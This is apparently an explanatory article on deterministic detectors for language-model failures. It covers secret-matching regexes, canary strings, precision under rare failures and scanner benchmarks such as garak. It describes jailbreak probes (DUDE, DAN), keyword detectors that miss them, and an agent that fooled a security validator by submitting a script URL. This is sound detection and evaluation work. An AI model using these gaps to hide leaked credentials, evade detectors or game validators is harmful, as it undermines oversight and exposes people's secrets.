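# Deterministic detectors for language-model failures: text patterns, canary strings and tool-call logs

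## What is a deterministic detector, and how is its quality measured?

A deterministic detector is a fixed rule that always gives the same verdict on the same recorded input. Engineers use such rules to find failures of language models, the programs behind chatbots and coding assistants. The approach suits failures that leave a definite trace, either in the model's answer or in the records of the software around it, that an ordinary program can find without any interpretation.

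The simplest rules are text patterns, which are substrings or regular expressions (a compact notation for a set of strings) that a program searches for. In 2021, GitHub gave its access tokens recognisable prefixes, such as `ghp_` for personal access tokens. A one-line search can find `ghp_` followed by 36 letters and digits in a coding assistant's answer, and a match probably means that somebody's credentials have leaked.

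A canary string is a unique random string placed in text that should never be copied, so that its appearance anywhere else is evidence of a leak. For example, a company might put one in its chatbot's hidden instructions. If a user then gets the chatbot to produce an answer containing the string, an exact search will detect a prompt leak, meaning an answer that reveals those instructions.

Many models can now also act by making tool calls, which are structured requests to run a program, for example to send an email or query a database. A model that can do this is called an agent. The harness is the software that prompts the model, reads its output, runs its tool calls and records them. The tool-call log is the harness's record of each call, with its arguments and result, and the trace is the full record of one run, including the model's text. In *ClawEnvKit* (2026), a system that generates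 test environments for agents, a logged email appears as `send_email(to="pm@company.com", ...)` followed by a status code. If the agent may write only to addresses at that company, a rule that compares the domain in the `to` field with the company's domain will find every logged email call that breaks the policy.

Computer security has used such detectors for decades. In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), Axelsson distinguished signature detection, where the defender decides in advance what bad behaviour looks like, from anomaly detection, which flags whatever is unusual. He wrote that signatures should catch known attacks quickly but have difficulty with new ones and need frequent updates. Both points also apply to detecting language-model failures.

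The alternatives to deterministic detectors use less exact criteria. A trained classifier is a statistical model fitted to labelled examples. It scores each new text, and a threshold determines which scores count as failures. Advani (2026), in *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure*, built small classifiers from word frequencies to find agents that falsely claim to have finished a task. Embedding similarity converts each text into a list of numbers, with similar lists for texts of similar meaning, and flags an answer whose list is close to that of a known bad example. An LLM judge is a language model asked to decide whether an output or a trace shows a failure.

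A classifier with frozen weights will usually return the same score for the same text, so it can also meet the definition of deterministic. A written rule differs in that a person can read it and say exactly what it matches, but this also limits what it can express. *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?* (2026) divides the work along these lines, using fixed checks for tool arguments, execution results and changes to the environment, and an LLM judge when the verdict depends on what a request or an action means. *Willful Disobedience* (2026), which is about finding rule violations in agents' traces, makes a similar distinction between checking the syntax of a data file and judging the tone of a reply.

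### Repeatable, valid, complete

A deterministic check is repeatable, meaning it always gives the same result on the same record. Determinism does not guarantee that the check is valid (its result matches the failure of interest) or complete (it catches all such failures).

Repeatability is still a useful property of deterministic detectors such as substring searches, because LLM judges often lack it. Developers try to make judges repeatable by fixing the model version and setting the temperature, which controls randomness in the output, to zero. Yorke (2026), in *Behind Aggregate Scores*, did both when using GPT-4.1 to judge which of two answers was better. Rerunning the unchanged default setup on the same 500 prompts and answers moved the total score by about one point but changed the win, tie or loss outcome on 21.2% of prompts. Other studies found less instability. *The Coin Flip Judge?*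 (2026) found that 2.8% of verdicts from GPT-4o-mini and 7.9% from GPT-4.1-mini still flipped at temperature zero. Ayyagari (2026), in *Pinned and Still Unstable*, reran four judges ten times each and found flip rates from 0.13% to 9.7%, depending on the judge. He suspects rounding differences and the way cloud servers batch requests, though he did not isolate the cause.

A deterministic detector guarantees the same verdict only for the same record. Agents behave differently from one run to the next, so a fixed rule can return different verdicts on different runs. Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents* (2026) calculates that an agent that passes a test 75% of the time will pass three attempts in a row only about 42% of the time.

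Near-perfect repeatability does not guarantee validity. In *Reliability without Validity*, Norman, Rivera and Hughes (2026) tested 21 LLM judges and found two, Qwen 3 8B and Gemini 2.5 Flash, that scored above 0.95 for agreement with themselves on repeated trials but strongly favoured answers based on their position in the prompt. A judge that always picked the answer in position A would be a deterministic detector and, as they point out, would get a perfect score for repeatability, but it would be worthless.

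Real fixed rules go wrong in the same way. In a 2025 talk, *AI Agents for Offsec with Zero False Positives*, Dolan-Gavitt described ordinary code that his company, XBOW, uses to confirm security holes reported by AI agents. One validator tested for cross-site scripting, a flaw that lets an attacker run a script inside someone else's web page, by opening the address the agent submitted and looking for a pop-up message. The programmers had forgotten to restrict the type of address. An agent submitted one that was itself a small script, which produced the pop-up even though the site had no flaw, and the validator would have accepted that submission every time.

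Completeness depends on how many kinds of failure the rule's author thought of. In *Real-Time Detection and Repair of LLM Agent Failures* (2026), fixed checks caught 60% of an agent's failures, and 96% after coverage was added. Their authors wrote the checks after looking at failures in those same runs, so they rightly did not treat the result as a test. On the same 120 tasks with a different model, the checks caught 110 of 110 failures without retuning. This is strong evidence that the checks carry over to another model, but weaker evidence that they carry over to other kinds of tasks.

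### What a fixed rule needs

A fixed rule can find a failure only if the failure leaves a mark, something records the mark, and the rule covers the forms the mark can take.

Some failures leave nothing that a deterministic detector can reliably identify. GitHub's older tokens were strings of 40 hexadecimal characters, which looked like other encoded data, such as the hashes that programmers use to identify files. A pattern that matched every token would also have matched those hashes, so GitHub added prefixes to its newer tokens. With agents, the difficulty is often that a failed attempt changes nothing a script can inspect. *OpenAgentSafety* (Vijayvargiya, Soni and colleagues, 2025) scored agents with a script that inspected the files, databases and websites after each run, and also with an LLM judge that read the whole trace. For the model o3-mini, the script found unsafe behaviour in 32%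 of the tasks where the agent reached the point of risk, and the judge found it in 73%. Some of that gap must come from failed attempts that changed nothing on disk, and some may come from the judge's mistakes, but the two percentages alone aren't enough to work out how much each contributed.

A detector can catch a failure only if the developer applies it to a record that shows the failure. An agent may state in its closing message that it has booked a flight, but the outcome, as Anthropic puts it, is whether the reservation exists in the database. Testing that outcome requires a state check, which compares the environment after a run (files, database rows, sent messages) with what it should be, rather than a rule that searches the message. Rules that read tool-call logs can also miss actions. If an agent sends email by running a script in a command shell, the log contains a shell call,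 and a rule that reads only `send_email` entries will miss the email.

A pattern can miss its target when the target's form changes. In February 2025 GitHub (2025) extended its scanner to tokens in Base64, a common encoding that turns a string into different characters with the same content. A pattern for the plain token does not match the encoded one. The following year GitHub (2026) warned that the tokens it issues to installed apps would grow from 40 characters to about 520, and that the pattern `ghs_[A-Za-z0-9]{36}` might no longer match. That pattern expects 36 letters and digits in a row after the prefix, but in the new format the prefix is followed by an app identifier and then an underscore, which interrupts the run. In May GitHub (2026) recommended a wider pattern that also allows dots, hyphens and underscores, and had to update that guidance within two weeks. A detector with the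 old pattern would have kept returning consistent verdicts throughout, and its lack of matches would have looked like a lack of tokens.

### Counting the errors

Measuring any detector's quality requires a set of cases whose true status is known. The detector's result on each case is then a true positive, a false positive, a true negative or a false negative.

| | Real failure | Harmless case |
|---|---|---|
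| Detector flags it | true positive (TP) | false positive (FP) |
| Detector passes it | false negative (FN) | true negative (TN) |

Precision is the share of alerts that are real failures, TP / (TP + FP). Recall is the share of real failures that the detector flags, TP / (TP + FN). The false-positive rate is the share of harmless cases that the detector flags, FP / (FP + TN). The base rate, which does not depend on the detector, is the share of all cases that are failures, (TP + FN) / (TP + FP + TN + FN).

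Writers use "false-positive rate" loosely, although its value depends heavily on the denominator. Axelsson defines the false-alarm rate over harmless events, but on the next page describes a 50% false-alarm rate among 100 alarms, which is a measure of precision. GitHub predicted that prefixes alone would bring its scanner's false-positive rate down to 0.5%, but did not say what the 0.5% was a share of.

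Kappa measures the agreement between two sets of labels beyond chance, for instance a detector's verdicts and a human reviewer's:

$$\kappa = \frac{p_o - p_e}{1 - p_e}$$

Here $p_o$ is the share of cases on which the two agree, and $p_e$ is the share on which they would agree by chance, given how often each uses each label. Kappa is zero when agreement is no better than chance and one when it is perfect. The correction can be large. Norman and colleagues calculate that a judge with 85% agreement on MT-Bench, a widely used test set of paired answers, has a kappa of only about 0.48.

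All these numbers depend on the quality of the labels. For *BARC-Bench* (2026), a test of whether agents act safely on harmless-looking requests, three people reviewed 300 traces, and any two of them agreed 93.3% of the time on average. A detector that matched one reviewer perfectly would still sometimes disagree with another. Labels can also be too easy to guess. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (Naagarajan and Streif, 2026) found that much of the reported success at spotting failed agent runs comes from regularities that can be detected without a model, such as failing runs being longer.

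### When failures are rare

Most answers from a deployed model are harmless, and this changes which detector is useful. In an invented example, 10 of 100,000 answers leak a secret. One detector is a classifier with high recall and a modest false-positive rate. The other is an exact check that finds only half the leaks but almost never flags a harmless answer.

| | Trained classifier | Exact check |
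|---|---|---|
| Recall | 0.95 | 0.5 |
| False-positive rate | 1 in 100 | 1 in 1,000,000 |
| Expected true alerts | 9.5 | 5 |
| Expected false alerts | about 1,000 | 0.1 |
| Precision | 0.9% | 98% |
| Expected leaks missed | 0.5 | 5 |
| Kappa | 0.02 | 0.66 |

The 99,990 harmless answers would produce about 1,000 false alerts at a false-positive rate of 1%, and an average of 0.1 at a rate of one in a million. At a minute per alert, a reviewer would spend almost 17 hours on the classifier's output to find nine or ten leaks. Accuracy is misleading here because a detector that never fires classifies 99.99% of these answers correctly, compared with about 99% for the classifier, even though its recall and kappa are both zero.

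In general, with recall $r$, false-positive rate $f$ and base rate $b$,

$$\text{precision} = \frac{r\,b}{r\,b + f\,(1-b)}$$

When $b$ is tiny, precision depends mostly on $f$. Axelsson calculated this for a small computer network with a million log records a day, 20 of them from intrusions. Even with perfect recall and a false-alarm rate of one in 100,000, only about 66% of alarms would be real. Cutting recall to 0.7 lowered that only to about 58%. He believed that operators would soon learn to ignore such a system. GitHub's *Making secret scanning more trustworthy* (2026) similarly reports that noisy alerts waste developers' time and erode their confidence. Naagarajan and Streif advise using their monitor of agent runs to rank runs for human review, since its precision stays low when failures are rare.

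By the same formula, a poor alarm can look very good in a published test. The same classifier from the table has a precision of 99% on a test set where half the cases are leaks. A precision figure therefore means little without the base rate at which it was measured.

Very low false-positive rates are also hard to establish by testing. The fixed checks in *Real-Time Detection and Repair of LLM Agent Failures* raised no false alarms on the second model, but that model produced only 10 successful runs, and zero in 10 is consistent with a true rate as high as about one in four. Supporting a claim of one in a million would take roughly three million harmless cases without an alert. A long random canary doesn't need this testing, because the chance of an accidental match can be calculated from its length.

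The two detectors miss different kinds of leaks, as well as different numbers of them. The classifier will miss one leak in twenty on average, probably one unlike any of its training examples, and a tired reviewer may overlook several more among the thousand false alerts. The exact check will miss leaks in forms its author did not specify, such as a token in Base64, a token broken across two lines, or a password with no fixed format. The exact check's misses are systematic, so an encoding that evades the rule once will evade it in every later answer, and running the check again will not reveal the gap.

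## How well do text patterns find leaked secrets?

A program can search a model's answers for leaked secrets in two ways. Known-value matching looks for specific strings, such as the passwords and API keys a company has on file. (An API key is a string that a program sends to an online service to show that it has permission to use the service.) Format matching looks for any string formatted like a key, whoever owns it.

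### Matching a known value

Known-value matching is by far the more precise method, because a long random string almost never appears by accident. There are $36^{16}$, or about $8 \times 10^{24}$, strings of 16 capital letters and digits. Even if a checker searched a billion answers, each made up of 10,000 random capitals and digits, the chance of finding a given string by accident would be roughly one in 800 billion. A match therefore shows that the secret got into the answer, although the company may have since revoked it or the reader may be entitled to it.

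Searching a model's output for a secret only works if the secret is hard to guess. If a company's password is `sunshine`, the detector will raise a false alert whenever the company's chatbot uses that word to describe the weather.

The main drawback is that the checker needs the secrets. Keeping all of a company's credentials in a chatbot's output filter creates an attractive target for theft. Storing hashes instead reduces the risk. A hash function turns a string into a short fingerprint, and nobody can feasibly recover a long random key from its fingerprint. But a hash represents a whole string, so the checker can't search an answer for it directly. It has to hash every stretch of the answer that is as long as the secret and compare each result with its list. For a 20-character key and a 4,000-character answer, that takes 3,981 hashes, and about as many again for each other secret length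 on the list.

Hashing also protects weak secrets poorly. A thief who has the hash of a six-digit code can hash all one million possible codes to find the match. The deliberately slow hash functions that websites use for login passwords would make this harder, but they are impractical when checking each answer takes thousands of hashes. A keyed hash, which mixes an extra secret into the calculation, stops the thief only if the extra secret is stored where the thief can't reach it but the checker can.

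Finally, a company can only list the secrets it knows about. If its chatbot repeats a key that a customer pasted into a document, or one that the model memorised in training, only format matching can find it.

### Matching a format

The regular expression `AKIA[0-9A-Z]{16}`, for example, finds access key IDs for Amazon's cloud service, AWS, by matching the letters AKIA followed by 16 digits or capital letters. *How Bad Can It Git?* (Meli, McNiece and Reaves, 2019) used it, along with patterns for 18 other types of key, to search public code on GitHub. The fixed prefix prevents most false matches, since without it the expression would match any run of 16 capitals and digits. Requiring 16 capitals or digits after the prefix rules out most of the ordinary text that happens to contain AKIA.

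The expression also matches `AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE`, a sample key in Amazon's documentation that gives no access to anything. It misses every ordinary password, since it matches only AKIA followed by 16 capitals and digits. It also matches only the ID in an AWS credential. Sensitive requests to AWS need a second string, the secret access key, which has no distinctive format. A match on the ID is still a useful warning, because Meli and colleagues found that at least 80% of the files with one part of a multi-part credential in their sample of newly uploaded files had another part within five lines.

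Many scanners next test whether the string looks random, using Shannon entropy:

$$H = -\sum_i p_i \log_2 p_i$$

Here $p_i$ is the share of the string's characters that are character $i$. A string of one repeated letter scores 0 bits per character, and a string of 20 different characters scores 4.32. The test works less well than one might expect on strings this short:

| String | What it is | Entropy (bits per character) |
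|---|---|---|
| `AKIAXXXEXAMPLEKEYXXX` | crude placeholder | 2.76 |
| `AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE` | Amazon's sample key | 3.68 |
| `AKIAIMW6ASF43DFX57X9` | plausible real key | 3.78 |

A threshold of 3 bits removes the crude placeholder and keeps Amazon's sample. A threshold between 3.68 and 3.78 would separate the other two, but it would also discard many genuine keys, because the scores of random 20-character keys vary by more than 0.1 bits. This problem arises because the formula counts how often each character occurs and ignores the order. In *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools*, Basak, Cox and colleagues (2023) give the example of `ThisIsAReallyLongString`, which scores about 4.1 bits, the same as a random-looking string of 47 letters and digits. The file hashes that looked like GitHub's old tokens often pass this test too, since they are close to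 random.

A word list does better on Amazon's sample key, which it rejects because the key contains the word EXAMPLE. Meli and colleagues rejected any match that contained a common word of five or more letters, or a run of four repeated or consecutive characters such as XXXX or ABCD. This filter will occasionally reject a real key that spells a word by chance.

Some issuers build a better test into their tokens. GitHub's `ghp_` tokens end in a six-character checksum, which anyone can recalculate from the rest of the token without contacting GitHub. Only one of about 57 billion possible endings is right, so a token that a language model invented for a tutorial will almost certainly fail. A correct checksum shows that a token is well formed, but not that GitHub issued it.

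### Testing whether the key works

The remaining step is to try the credential. TruffleHog, an open-source scanner, checks AWS credentials by sending Amazon a request that returns the account they belong to. When Basak and colleagues set it to report only credentials that passed such tests, its precision rose from 6% to 90%, and its alerts fell from almost 100,000 to 611. That implies about 550 correct alerts, compared with 5,426 before. Many of the lost alerts were presumably for keys that had been revoked or that TruffleHog couldn't test, but the figures don't separate these cases. TruffleHog also misses a working key if it can't reach the issuer's server. Some of its remaining false alerts were for dummy web addresses with "password" in the password field.

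Unlike the other steps, live testing sends the secret over the network and uses somebody else's account. Meli and colleagues never tried any key they found, partly because a single request might cost the owner money or use up a quota. Live testing also stops the detector being deterministic. A log that triggers an alert on Monday will pass on Tuesday if the owner revokes the key overnight, even though the log hasn't changed. It therefore makes sense to store the live test result separately from the format match, and to record the date of the test.

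### The characters on either side

A pattern can also match part of a longer string that isn't a key. *Decoding Secret Memorization in Code LLMs Through Token-Level Characterization* (2024) gives the example of a long string whose middle matches the format of a Google API key, although the letters on either side show that it isn't one. To avoid such matches, Meli and colleagues rejected any match with a letter, digit or underscore directly before or after it.

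Such rules can be too strict. Mishra (2026), in *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, generated artificial keys from each rule's regular expression and placed them in different surroundings, such as inside quotation marks or as a function argument. The study mainly tested Mishra's own open-source scanner, which has 43 rules. The scanner found at least 99.76% of the keys in ten kinds of surroundings, but only 52.33% of those that ended in a hyphen. The cause was `\b`, the regular-expression code for a word boundary, which matches the edge between a word character and anything else. Neither a hyphen nor a closing quotation mark is a word character, so there is no such edge between them. Rules for fixed-length keys therefore missed the key entirely, while rules for variable-length keys went back to an earlier edge and reported a truncated key.

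For one common type of token, this bug would affect one token in 64, so a developer who tests a rule on two or three examples is unlikely to notice it. Mishra's first fix looked reasonable but broke two rules in cases that had worked before. Gitleaks, a popular open-source scanner, had a different fault. It accepts a key only if the next character is on a fixed list, so it missed keys of six of the nine types it otherwise detects. In a chatbot's answer, the next character could easily be a full stop, or an asterisk or backtick used for formatting. Mishra tested source code, so anyone who applies such a scanner to answers should repeat the test with those characters.

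Chatbots usually stream an answer in small chunks while the model is still writing it, which can also split a secret. If one chunk ends in `AKIAIOSFOD` and the next begins with `NN7EXAMPLE`, a checker that searches each chunk separately will miss the 20-character key. To find it, the checker has to keep the last 19 characters of the answer so far and put them in front of each new chunk, because up to 19 characters of the key may already have arrived. Those 19 characters may span several chunks, since a chunk may be only a few characters long. A 40-character GitHub token requires keeping 39 characters, and a rule that also inspects the neighbouring characters requires slightly more.

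Without this buffer, the same answer can pass or fail depending on where the server splits it. Even with the buffer, the user may have read the first 19 characters of the key before the last one arrives, so a checker meant to block leaks has to hold back the most recent 19 characters until more text comes or the answer ends.

### Precision and recall on source code

Basak and colleagues compared nine scanners on *SecretBench* (2023), a dataset drawn from 818 public GitHub repositories. Its compilers used 761 patterns to find 97,479 candidate strings. Two of the compilers labelled the candidates by hand and judged 15,084 to be real secrets, of which 4,457 were distinct. In the table, recall is the share of these distinct secrets that a scanner reported anywhere in the right repository.

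| Scanner | Alerts | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub secret scanner | 1,721 | 75% | 36% |
| Gitleaks | 45,932 | 46% | 88% |
| Commercial X (anonymous product) | 86,607 | 25% | 48% |
| ggshield | 167,046 | 19% | 46% |
| TruffleHog, without live tests | 90,982 | 6% | 52% |
| git-secrets | 94,491 | 5% | 21% |
| Repo-supervisor | 181,310 | 2% | 17% |
| Whispers | 416,516 | 0.6% | 38% |
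| SpectralOps | 1,547,994 | 0.3% | 67% |

No scanner did well on both precision and recall. Three out of four alerts from GitHub's scanner were correct, but it missed almost two thirds of the secrets. SpectralOps found two thirds of the secrets, but fewer than one in 300 of its alerts was correct.

Gitleaks and TruffleHog probably perform worse than their results suggest, because SecretBench used those two tools to find its candidates. A secret that both tools missed isn't in the dataset, so it can't lower their recall. If another scanner finds such a secret, the match counts as a false positive. Recall also depends on how strictly matches are scored. When Basak and colleagues required the exact version, file and line, TruffleHog's recall fell from 52% to 31%, and the recall of GitHub's scanner fell from 36% to 3%.

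Most of the false positives examined came from loose patterns. One scanner flagged any name that ended in "key" or "token", such as `testkey`. Others flagged the opening line of a private key even when no key followed. TruffleHog treated any run of 20 to 22 suitable characters near the word "gitlab" as a GitLab token, so it flagged `add-a-file-using-the-` in the address of a help page. Scanners often missed secrets for equally simple reasons, such as having no rule for the service or skipping web pages entirely.

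Meli and colleagues got very different results. They classed between 98.9% and 99.3% of the strings that matched their patterns as valid keys. The rate was this high because they searched only for 19 types of key with very distinctive formats and left out passwords, which can be almost any string. Their test of validity was also weak, since a match only had to pass their own entropy, word and sequence filters. A program can verify the internal structure of a private RSA key, a common type of encryption key, and when the researchers checked one sample this way, they found that the filters had rejected only 17 of 67 invalid keys. However, those 67 were among 25,437 matches, so the pattern itself was right 99.7% of the time. A manual review of 240 AWS and RSA matches also found only four that weren't valid keys.

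It seems that a narrow pattern for a distinctive key is very precise and a general search for "secrets" is not. Meli and colleagues could not calculate recall because nobody has a full list of the secrets on GitHub. Also, not every valid key is worth an alert. From the manual review, they estimated that about 94% of the API keys and 76% of the private keys were sensitive. The others included keys that developers had made for testing.

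Rankings of scanners also deserve some caution. Mishra compared three scanners on ten types of credential and found no statistically significant difference in recall. A fixed rule treats nearly all keys of one type alike, so 400 keys of ten types amount to only ten observations.

Recall also depends on where the scanner looks. Gorijala (2026), in *Secrets That Survive Everything*, tested nine scanners on 194 credentials in the JavaScript that one organisation's websites sent to visitors' browsers. The best scanner that only read the files found 36.6%. The best one that also took account of what the code does when it runs found 77.8%, partly because it could decrypt settings whose key was in the same file. All nine missed 27 of the credentials. Gorijala built the answer key with help from two language models and declares a conflict of interest as the developer of one of the tools, so the ranking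 needs independent confirmation. Regardless of the ranking, text patterns can't match credentials in settings that are still encrypted.

### Patterns compared with trained models

The case for using a trained model is clearest for passwords. *Tales from the Git* (2023) rejects patterns and entropy for finding them, because passwords have no fixed structure and many people choose weak ones. It uses two neural networks instead, one to classify the string and one to classify the code around it.

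For other secrets, researchers often use a language model to check what the patterns flag. *Secret Breach Detection in Source Code with Large Language Models* (2025) used a fine-tuned version of LLaMA 3.1 8B, a small model from Meta, to classify 3,000 strings that patterns had already flagged. Its F1 score, which combines precision and recall, was 0.985. The paper compares this with a precision of 50% for patterns alone, but that figure follows from the test's design, since half of the flagged strings were secrets. The test shows that a model can filter out a pattern's false alarms, but not how many secrets the patterns missed, because the model never received those. *Argus* (2025) similarly has a language model weigh a pattern match as evidence instead of treating every match as a secret.

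OpenAI's Privacy Filter is a small classifier that labels personal data and secrets in text, without a pattern-matching step first. The *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter* (de Bourcy, Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, 2026) reports 96.5% recall and 74.7% precision on CredData, a set of credentials in code. These figures are based on tokens, the short pieces of text that language models process, rather than whole secrets, so they aren't directly comparable with the table above.

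They also tested the classifier on invented sentences, which showed how much it depends on context. It found 71% of secrets when an explanation such as "my password is" came first, 42% when the explanation came afterwards, and 36% when the secret stood alone. A pattern for AWS keys gives the same result in all three cases, but it would miss most of what people put after "my password is".

### Model answers and agent logs

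The studies of scanners all tested them on code, and the same rules may do better or worse on a chatbot's answers. Code scanners use clues such as file types and variable names, which an answer may lack. Models often write example code with made-up keys, which should increase false alerts. A user can also ask a model to rewrite a secret in another form, whereas most developers who leak a key into code paste it unchanged. Basak, Meli, Mishra and their colleagues did not measure any of these effects.

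Li, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills*, studied 48,682 skills, which are packages of instructions and code that people download to extend an agent. The instructions mix prose and commands, much as a chatbot's answer does. One pattern looked for instructions to put a secret into the computer's environment settings, where other programs can read it. It matched 2,232 skills, largely because it also matched security warnings and placeholders. The researchers checked 93 matches from this pattern and two similar ones, and none was genuine. A pattern for a risky download command was right 95% of the time under an installation heading but 48% of the time elsewhere in the same files. Since precision varied this much within the same files, it can also differ between code and conversation.

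Li and colleagues also looked for skills that print credentials, since an agent's harness passes printed text back to the model. Their program traced credentials to print commands and searched the nearby lines for signs of a key. It flagged 433 skills, and a manual check found real leaks in 22 of them, or 5.1%. Most of the others printed something harmless, such as a file path or the name of a credential. In another 2,075 skills, the program traced a credential to a print command but found no sign of a key nearby. A sample of 100 of these contained six real leaks, which suggests about 125 in total. Searching nearby lines therefore probably missed several times as many leaks as it found, usually because the skill read the secret in a different part of the code. The program searched only the skills' code, and searching what the skills print when they run could give different results.

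Studies of agents' own text have mostly counted pattern matches. *Agents in the Wild* (2026) searched posts on Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, and found 572 strings in the format of an API key, from 101 agents. Without a checksum or a live test, 572 is an upper limit on the number of working keys of those types, which could be far lower. *AgentLeak* (2026), which looks for private data in traces, reports false alerts from internal ticket numbers in the same format as US social security numbers.

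Agent logs also contain keys that were used legitimately, because an agent that queries a paid service has to send its key and the log may record it. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) defines a leak as the exposure of a credential to a recipient that the skill neither declares nor needs for its stated purpose. A pattern can find the key in a log, but applying that definition also requires a list of the recipients allowed to receive the key.

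Software that cleans logs has the opposite problem, since it also has to remove secrets it can't recognise. *NovaFabric* (2026), a recorder for agent runs, removes secrets with a set of Gitleaks rules before it saves the files, then scans the result again. According to its documentation, the rules don't cover private keys in PEM format, passwords, database connection strings and several other kinds of credential. A second scan with the same rules can confirm that the first removed what it found, but any password the rules don't match will stay in the log.

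### Encoded and altered text

A literal match fails if the answer contains the secret in another form, such as in Base64 or with spaces between the characters. If the secret is a sentence rather than a random key, a translation or paraphrase can reveal all of it without repeating any of its words.

Developers can catch some of these cases by normalising the text, or converting it to a standard form, before searching it. Typical steps are to replace look-alike characters with ordinary letters, delete invisible characters and spaces, ignore capitalisation, and decode anything that looks like Base64. Each step allows the search to find some altered secrets but also creates new accidental matches.

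Deleting spaces before matching, for example, can cause false alerts. The heading "AKIA PREFIX MARKS ACCESS KEYS" becomes `AKIAPREFIXMARKSACCESSKEYS`, and its first 20 characters match the AWS pattern. Rejecting any match followed directly by a letter would prevent this false alert, but it would also reject real keys that the deletion had joined to the next word.

Ignoring capitalisation causes even more false matches. In random Base64 text, the AWS pattern without boundary rules matches by accident about once in 170 billion characters. If it also accepts lower-case letters, it matches about once in 1.7 million. Agents' logs can contain whole images in Base64, so a large log could produce false alerts every day. It is safer to search the original text with the strict pattern, search the normalised text separately, and give matches in the normalised text a lower priority.

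Known-value matching has much less of this problem, because a long random key is still extremely unlikely to appear by chance even when the checker ignores spaces and capitals. The checker can also search for encoded versions of each secret. Base64 turns every three bytes into four characters, so a secret inside a longer encoded passage can take three forms, depending on where it starts. A program can work out all three in advance, except for a character or two at each end that depend on the neighbouring text. This search requires the secrets themselves or hashes of every form. It also covers only the encodings the developer thought of, and a user can always ask the model for another.

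Trained classifiers also make many errors on disguised text. De Bourcy and colleagues tested Privacy Filter on disguised personal data and secrets. With unusual spacing, its recall was 63% and its precision 70%. With line breaks inside the data, its recall was 81%, but more than half of what it flagged was wrong. It did better with look-alike characters, at 91% recall and 82% precision, but these are among the easiest disguises for a fixed rule to undo.

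## What goes wrong when word matching is used to judge meaning?

A text pattern misses a disguised key but can catch an undisguised one, because a rule can describe its form. Many other failures have no such form. GitHub could give its tokens a fixed prefix, but refusals have no set wording, and a model can give dangerous instructions in dry technical language. A search for "bomb" would flag a history lesson about the Blitz and miss a recipe that lists only chemicals and quantities.

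To detect a failure such as a refusal with a fixed rule, a developer has to pick words that tend to accompany it, such as "I'm sorry". The rule detects the words, and the developer infers the refusal from them. That inference depends on how the model usually phrases refusals, which varies between models and versions.

### From prompt to verdict in garak

garak is an open-source scanner that sends known attacks to a language model and checks whether they worked. Derczynski, Galinkin and colleagues (2024), in *garak*, describe how it imitates Nmap, a program that finds computers on a network by sending them data and analysing what comes back. A probe holds prompts meant to cause one kind of failure. A generator passes them to the model and returns its answers. A detector then scores each answer from 0 (no failure found) to 1 (failure found). Optional components called buffs alter the prompts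 first, for example by paraphrasing them. A harness pairs each probe with suitable detectors, and garak logs every prompt, answer and score.

A simple example is garak's DUDE probe, which sends a jailbreak, a prompt designed to make a model ignore its safety rules. The prompt asks the model to play DUDE, a character without restrictions. According to garak's documentation, a detector called `dan.DUDE` then searches the answer for one substring, `DUDE:`. If the answer contains it, garak reports that the model adopted the persona and that this may be a jailbreak. Otherwise, the model passes.

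In a 2024 test, one model said it would respond as DUDE would, with no ethical boundaries. Garak's detector did not flag the answer because it had no colon after the name. The documentation still lists `DUDE:` as the only substring the detector looks for, although garak leaves this probe off by default. The detector would also wrongly count "DUDE: I can't help with that" as a jailbreak. Dropping the colon from the pattern would fix the first error, but the detector would then flag any refusal that mentions DUDE.

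garak lists a second detector for the same probe, MitigationBypass, which works the other way round. It searches for refusal phrases and reports a failure when it finds none. garak's documentation traces these phrases to ChatGPT refusals in ShareGPT, a collection of conversations that the developers of Vicuna, an early open chatbot, used for training. The list therefore reflects how one company's older models refused.

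Because keyword detectors, like Axelsson's attack signatures, miss new problems, Derczynski and colleagues also gave garak trained classifiers.

### Two tests of the scanners

The DUDE error comes from an October 2024 comparison by Fujitsu researchers. They ran the scanners garak, Giskard, Microsoft's PyRIT and Meta's CyberSecEval against four models. CyberSecEval and garak relied mainly on patterns, while PyRIT and Giskard relied mainly on LLM judges. The researchers labelled 1,045 answers by hand as successful or failed attacks and compared these labels with the scanners' results.

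They reported a margin of error for each scanner, by type of attack and model. The largest margins were 26% for garak, 23% for PyRIT, 20% for CyberSecEval and 16% for Giskard. They equated garak's 26% margin with a 37% error rate in detecting successful attacks, and rated PyRIT the most reliable overall. The judges made a different kind of mistake. When a model refused to explain how to hack a school's computers, Giskard's judge marked the refusal as unsafe because it offered no way to report harmful content, a requirement that Giskard itself had generated.

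These numbers are rough. The researchers left out ambiguous answers, which probably made every scanner look better, and they tested each scanner on its own prompts. Some of garak's margins were as low as 0.05%, far too small to measure with the 60 labelled answers behind them. Those answers came from prompts asking for well-known test strings, a task that suits exact matching.

In *When Scanners Lie*, the same group (Erez, Hofman and colleagues, 2026) tested a newer version of garak. They ran 25 categories of attack against three models and collected about 23,000 answers. They scored these answers both with garak's default detectors, 82% of which were rule-based, and with Grok-4.1 as an LLM judge. The two methods disagreed on more than 5% of answers in 22 categories, and on more than half of answers in six of them. For those 22 categories, they used GPT-5.2 as a reference to estimate which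 method was right. The table shows a selection of the results.

| Attack category | Default detectors | Grok-4.1 as judge |
|---|---|---|
| Antivirus and spam test strings | 100% | 97.8% |
| Package hallucination (made-up software packages) | 90.3% | 96.3% |
| Leak replay (repeating training text) | 88.0% | 79.0% |
| Prompt injection | 79.7% | 91.0% |
| Harmful questions | 74.3% | 97.3% |
| DAN ("do anything now") jailbreaks | 65.7% | 92.3% |
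| Malware requests | 20.7% | 95.3% |
| Misleading claims | 2.0% | 93.7% |
| All 22 categories | 72.4% | 89.3% |

Two other judges, GPT-4o and Microsoft's small Phi-4, scored 85.3% and 82.0% overall. The default detectors still beat Grok-4.1 in four categories, including test strings and leak replay.

A language model, GPT-5.2, supplied the reference labels, so they may favour other language models. Only one person, the first author, checked any of the labels, agreeing with 93% of a sample of 200. In 10 of the 14 disagreements, GPT-5.2 had counted a failed attack as a success. Such errors probably can't explain an overall gap of 17 points, but the small gaps in single categories could easily be wrong.

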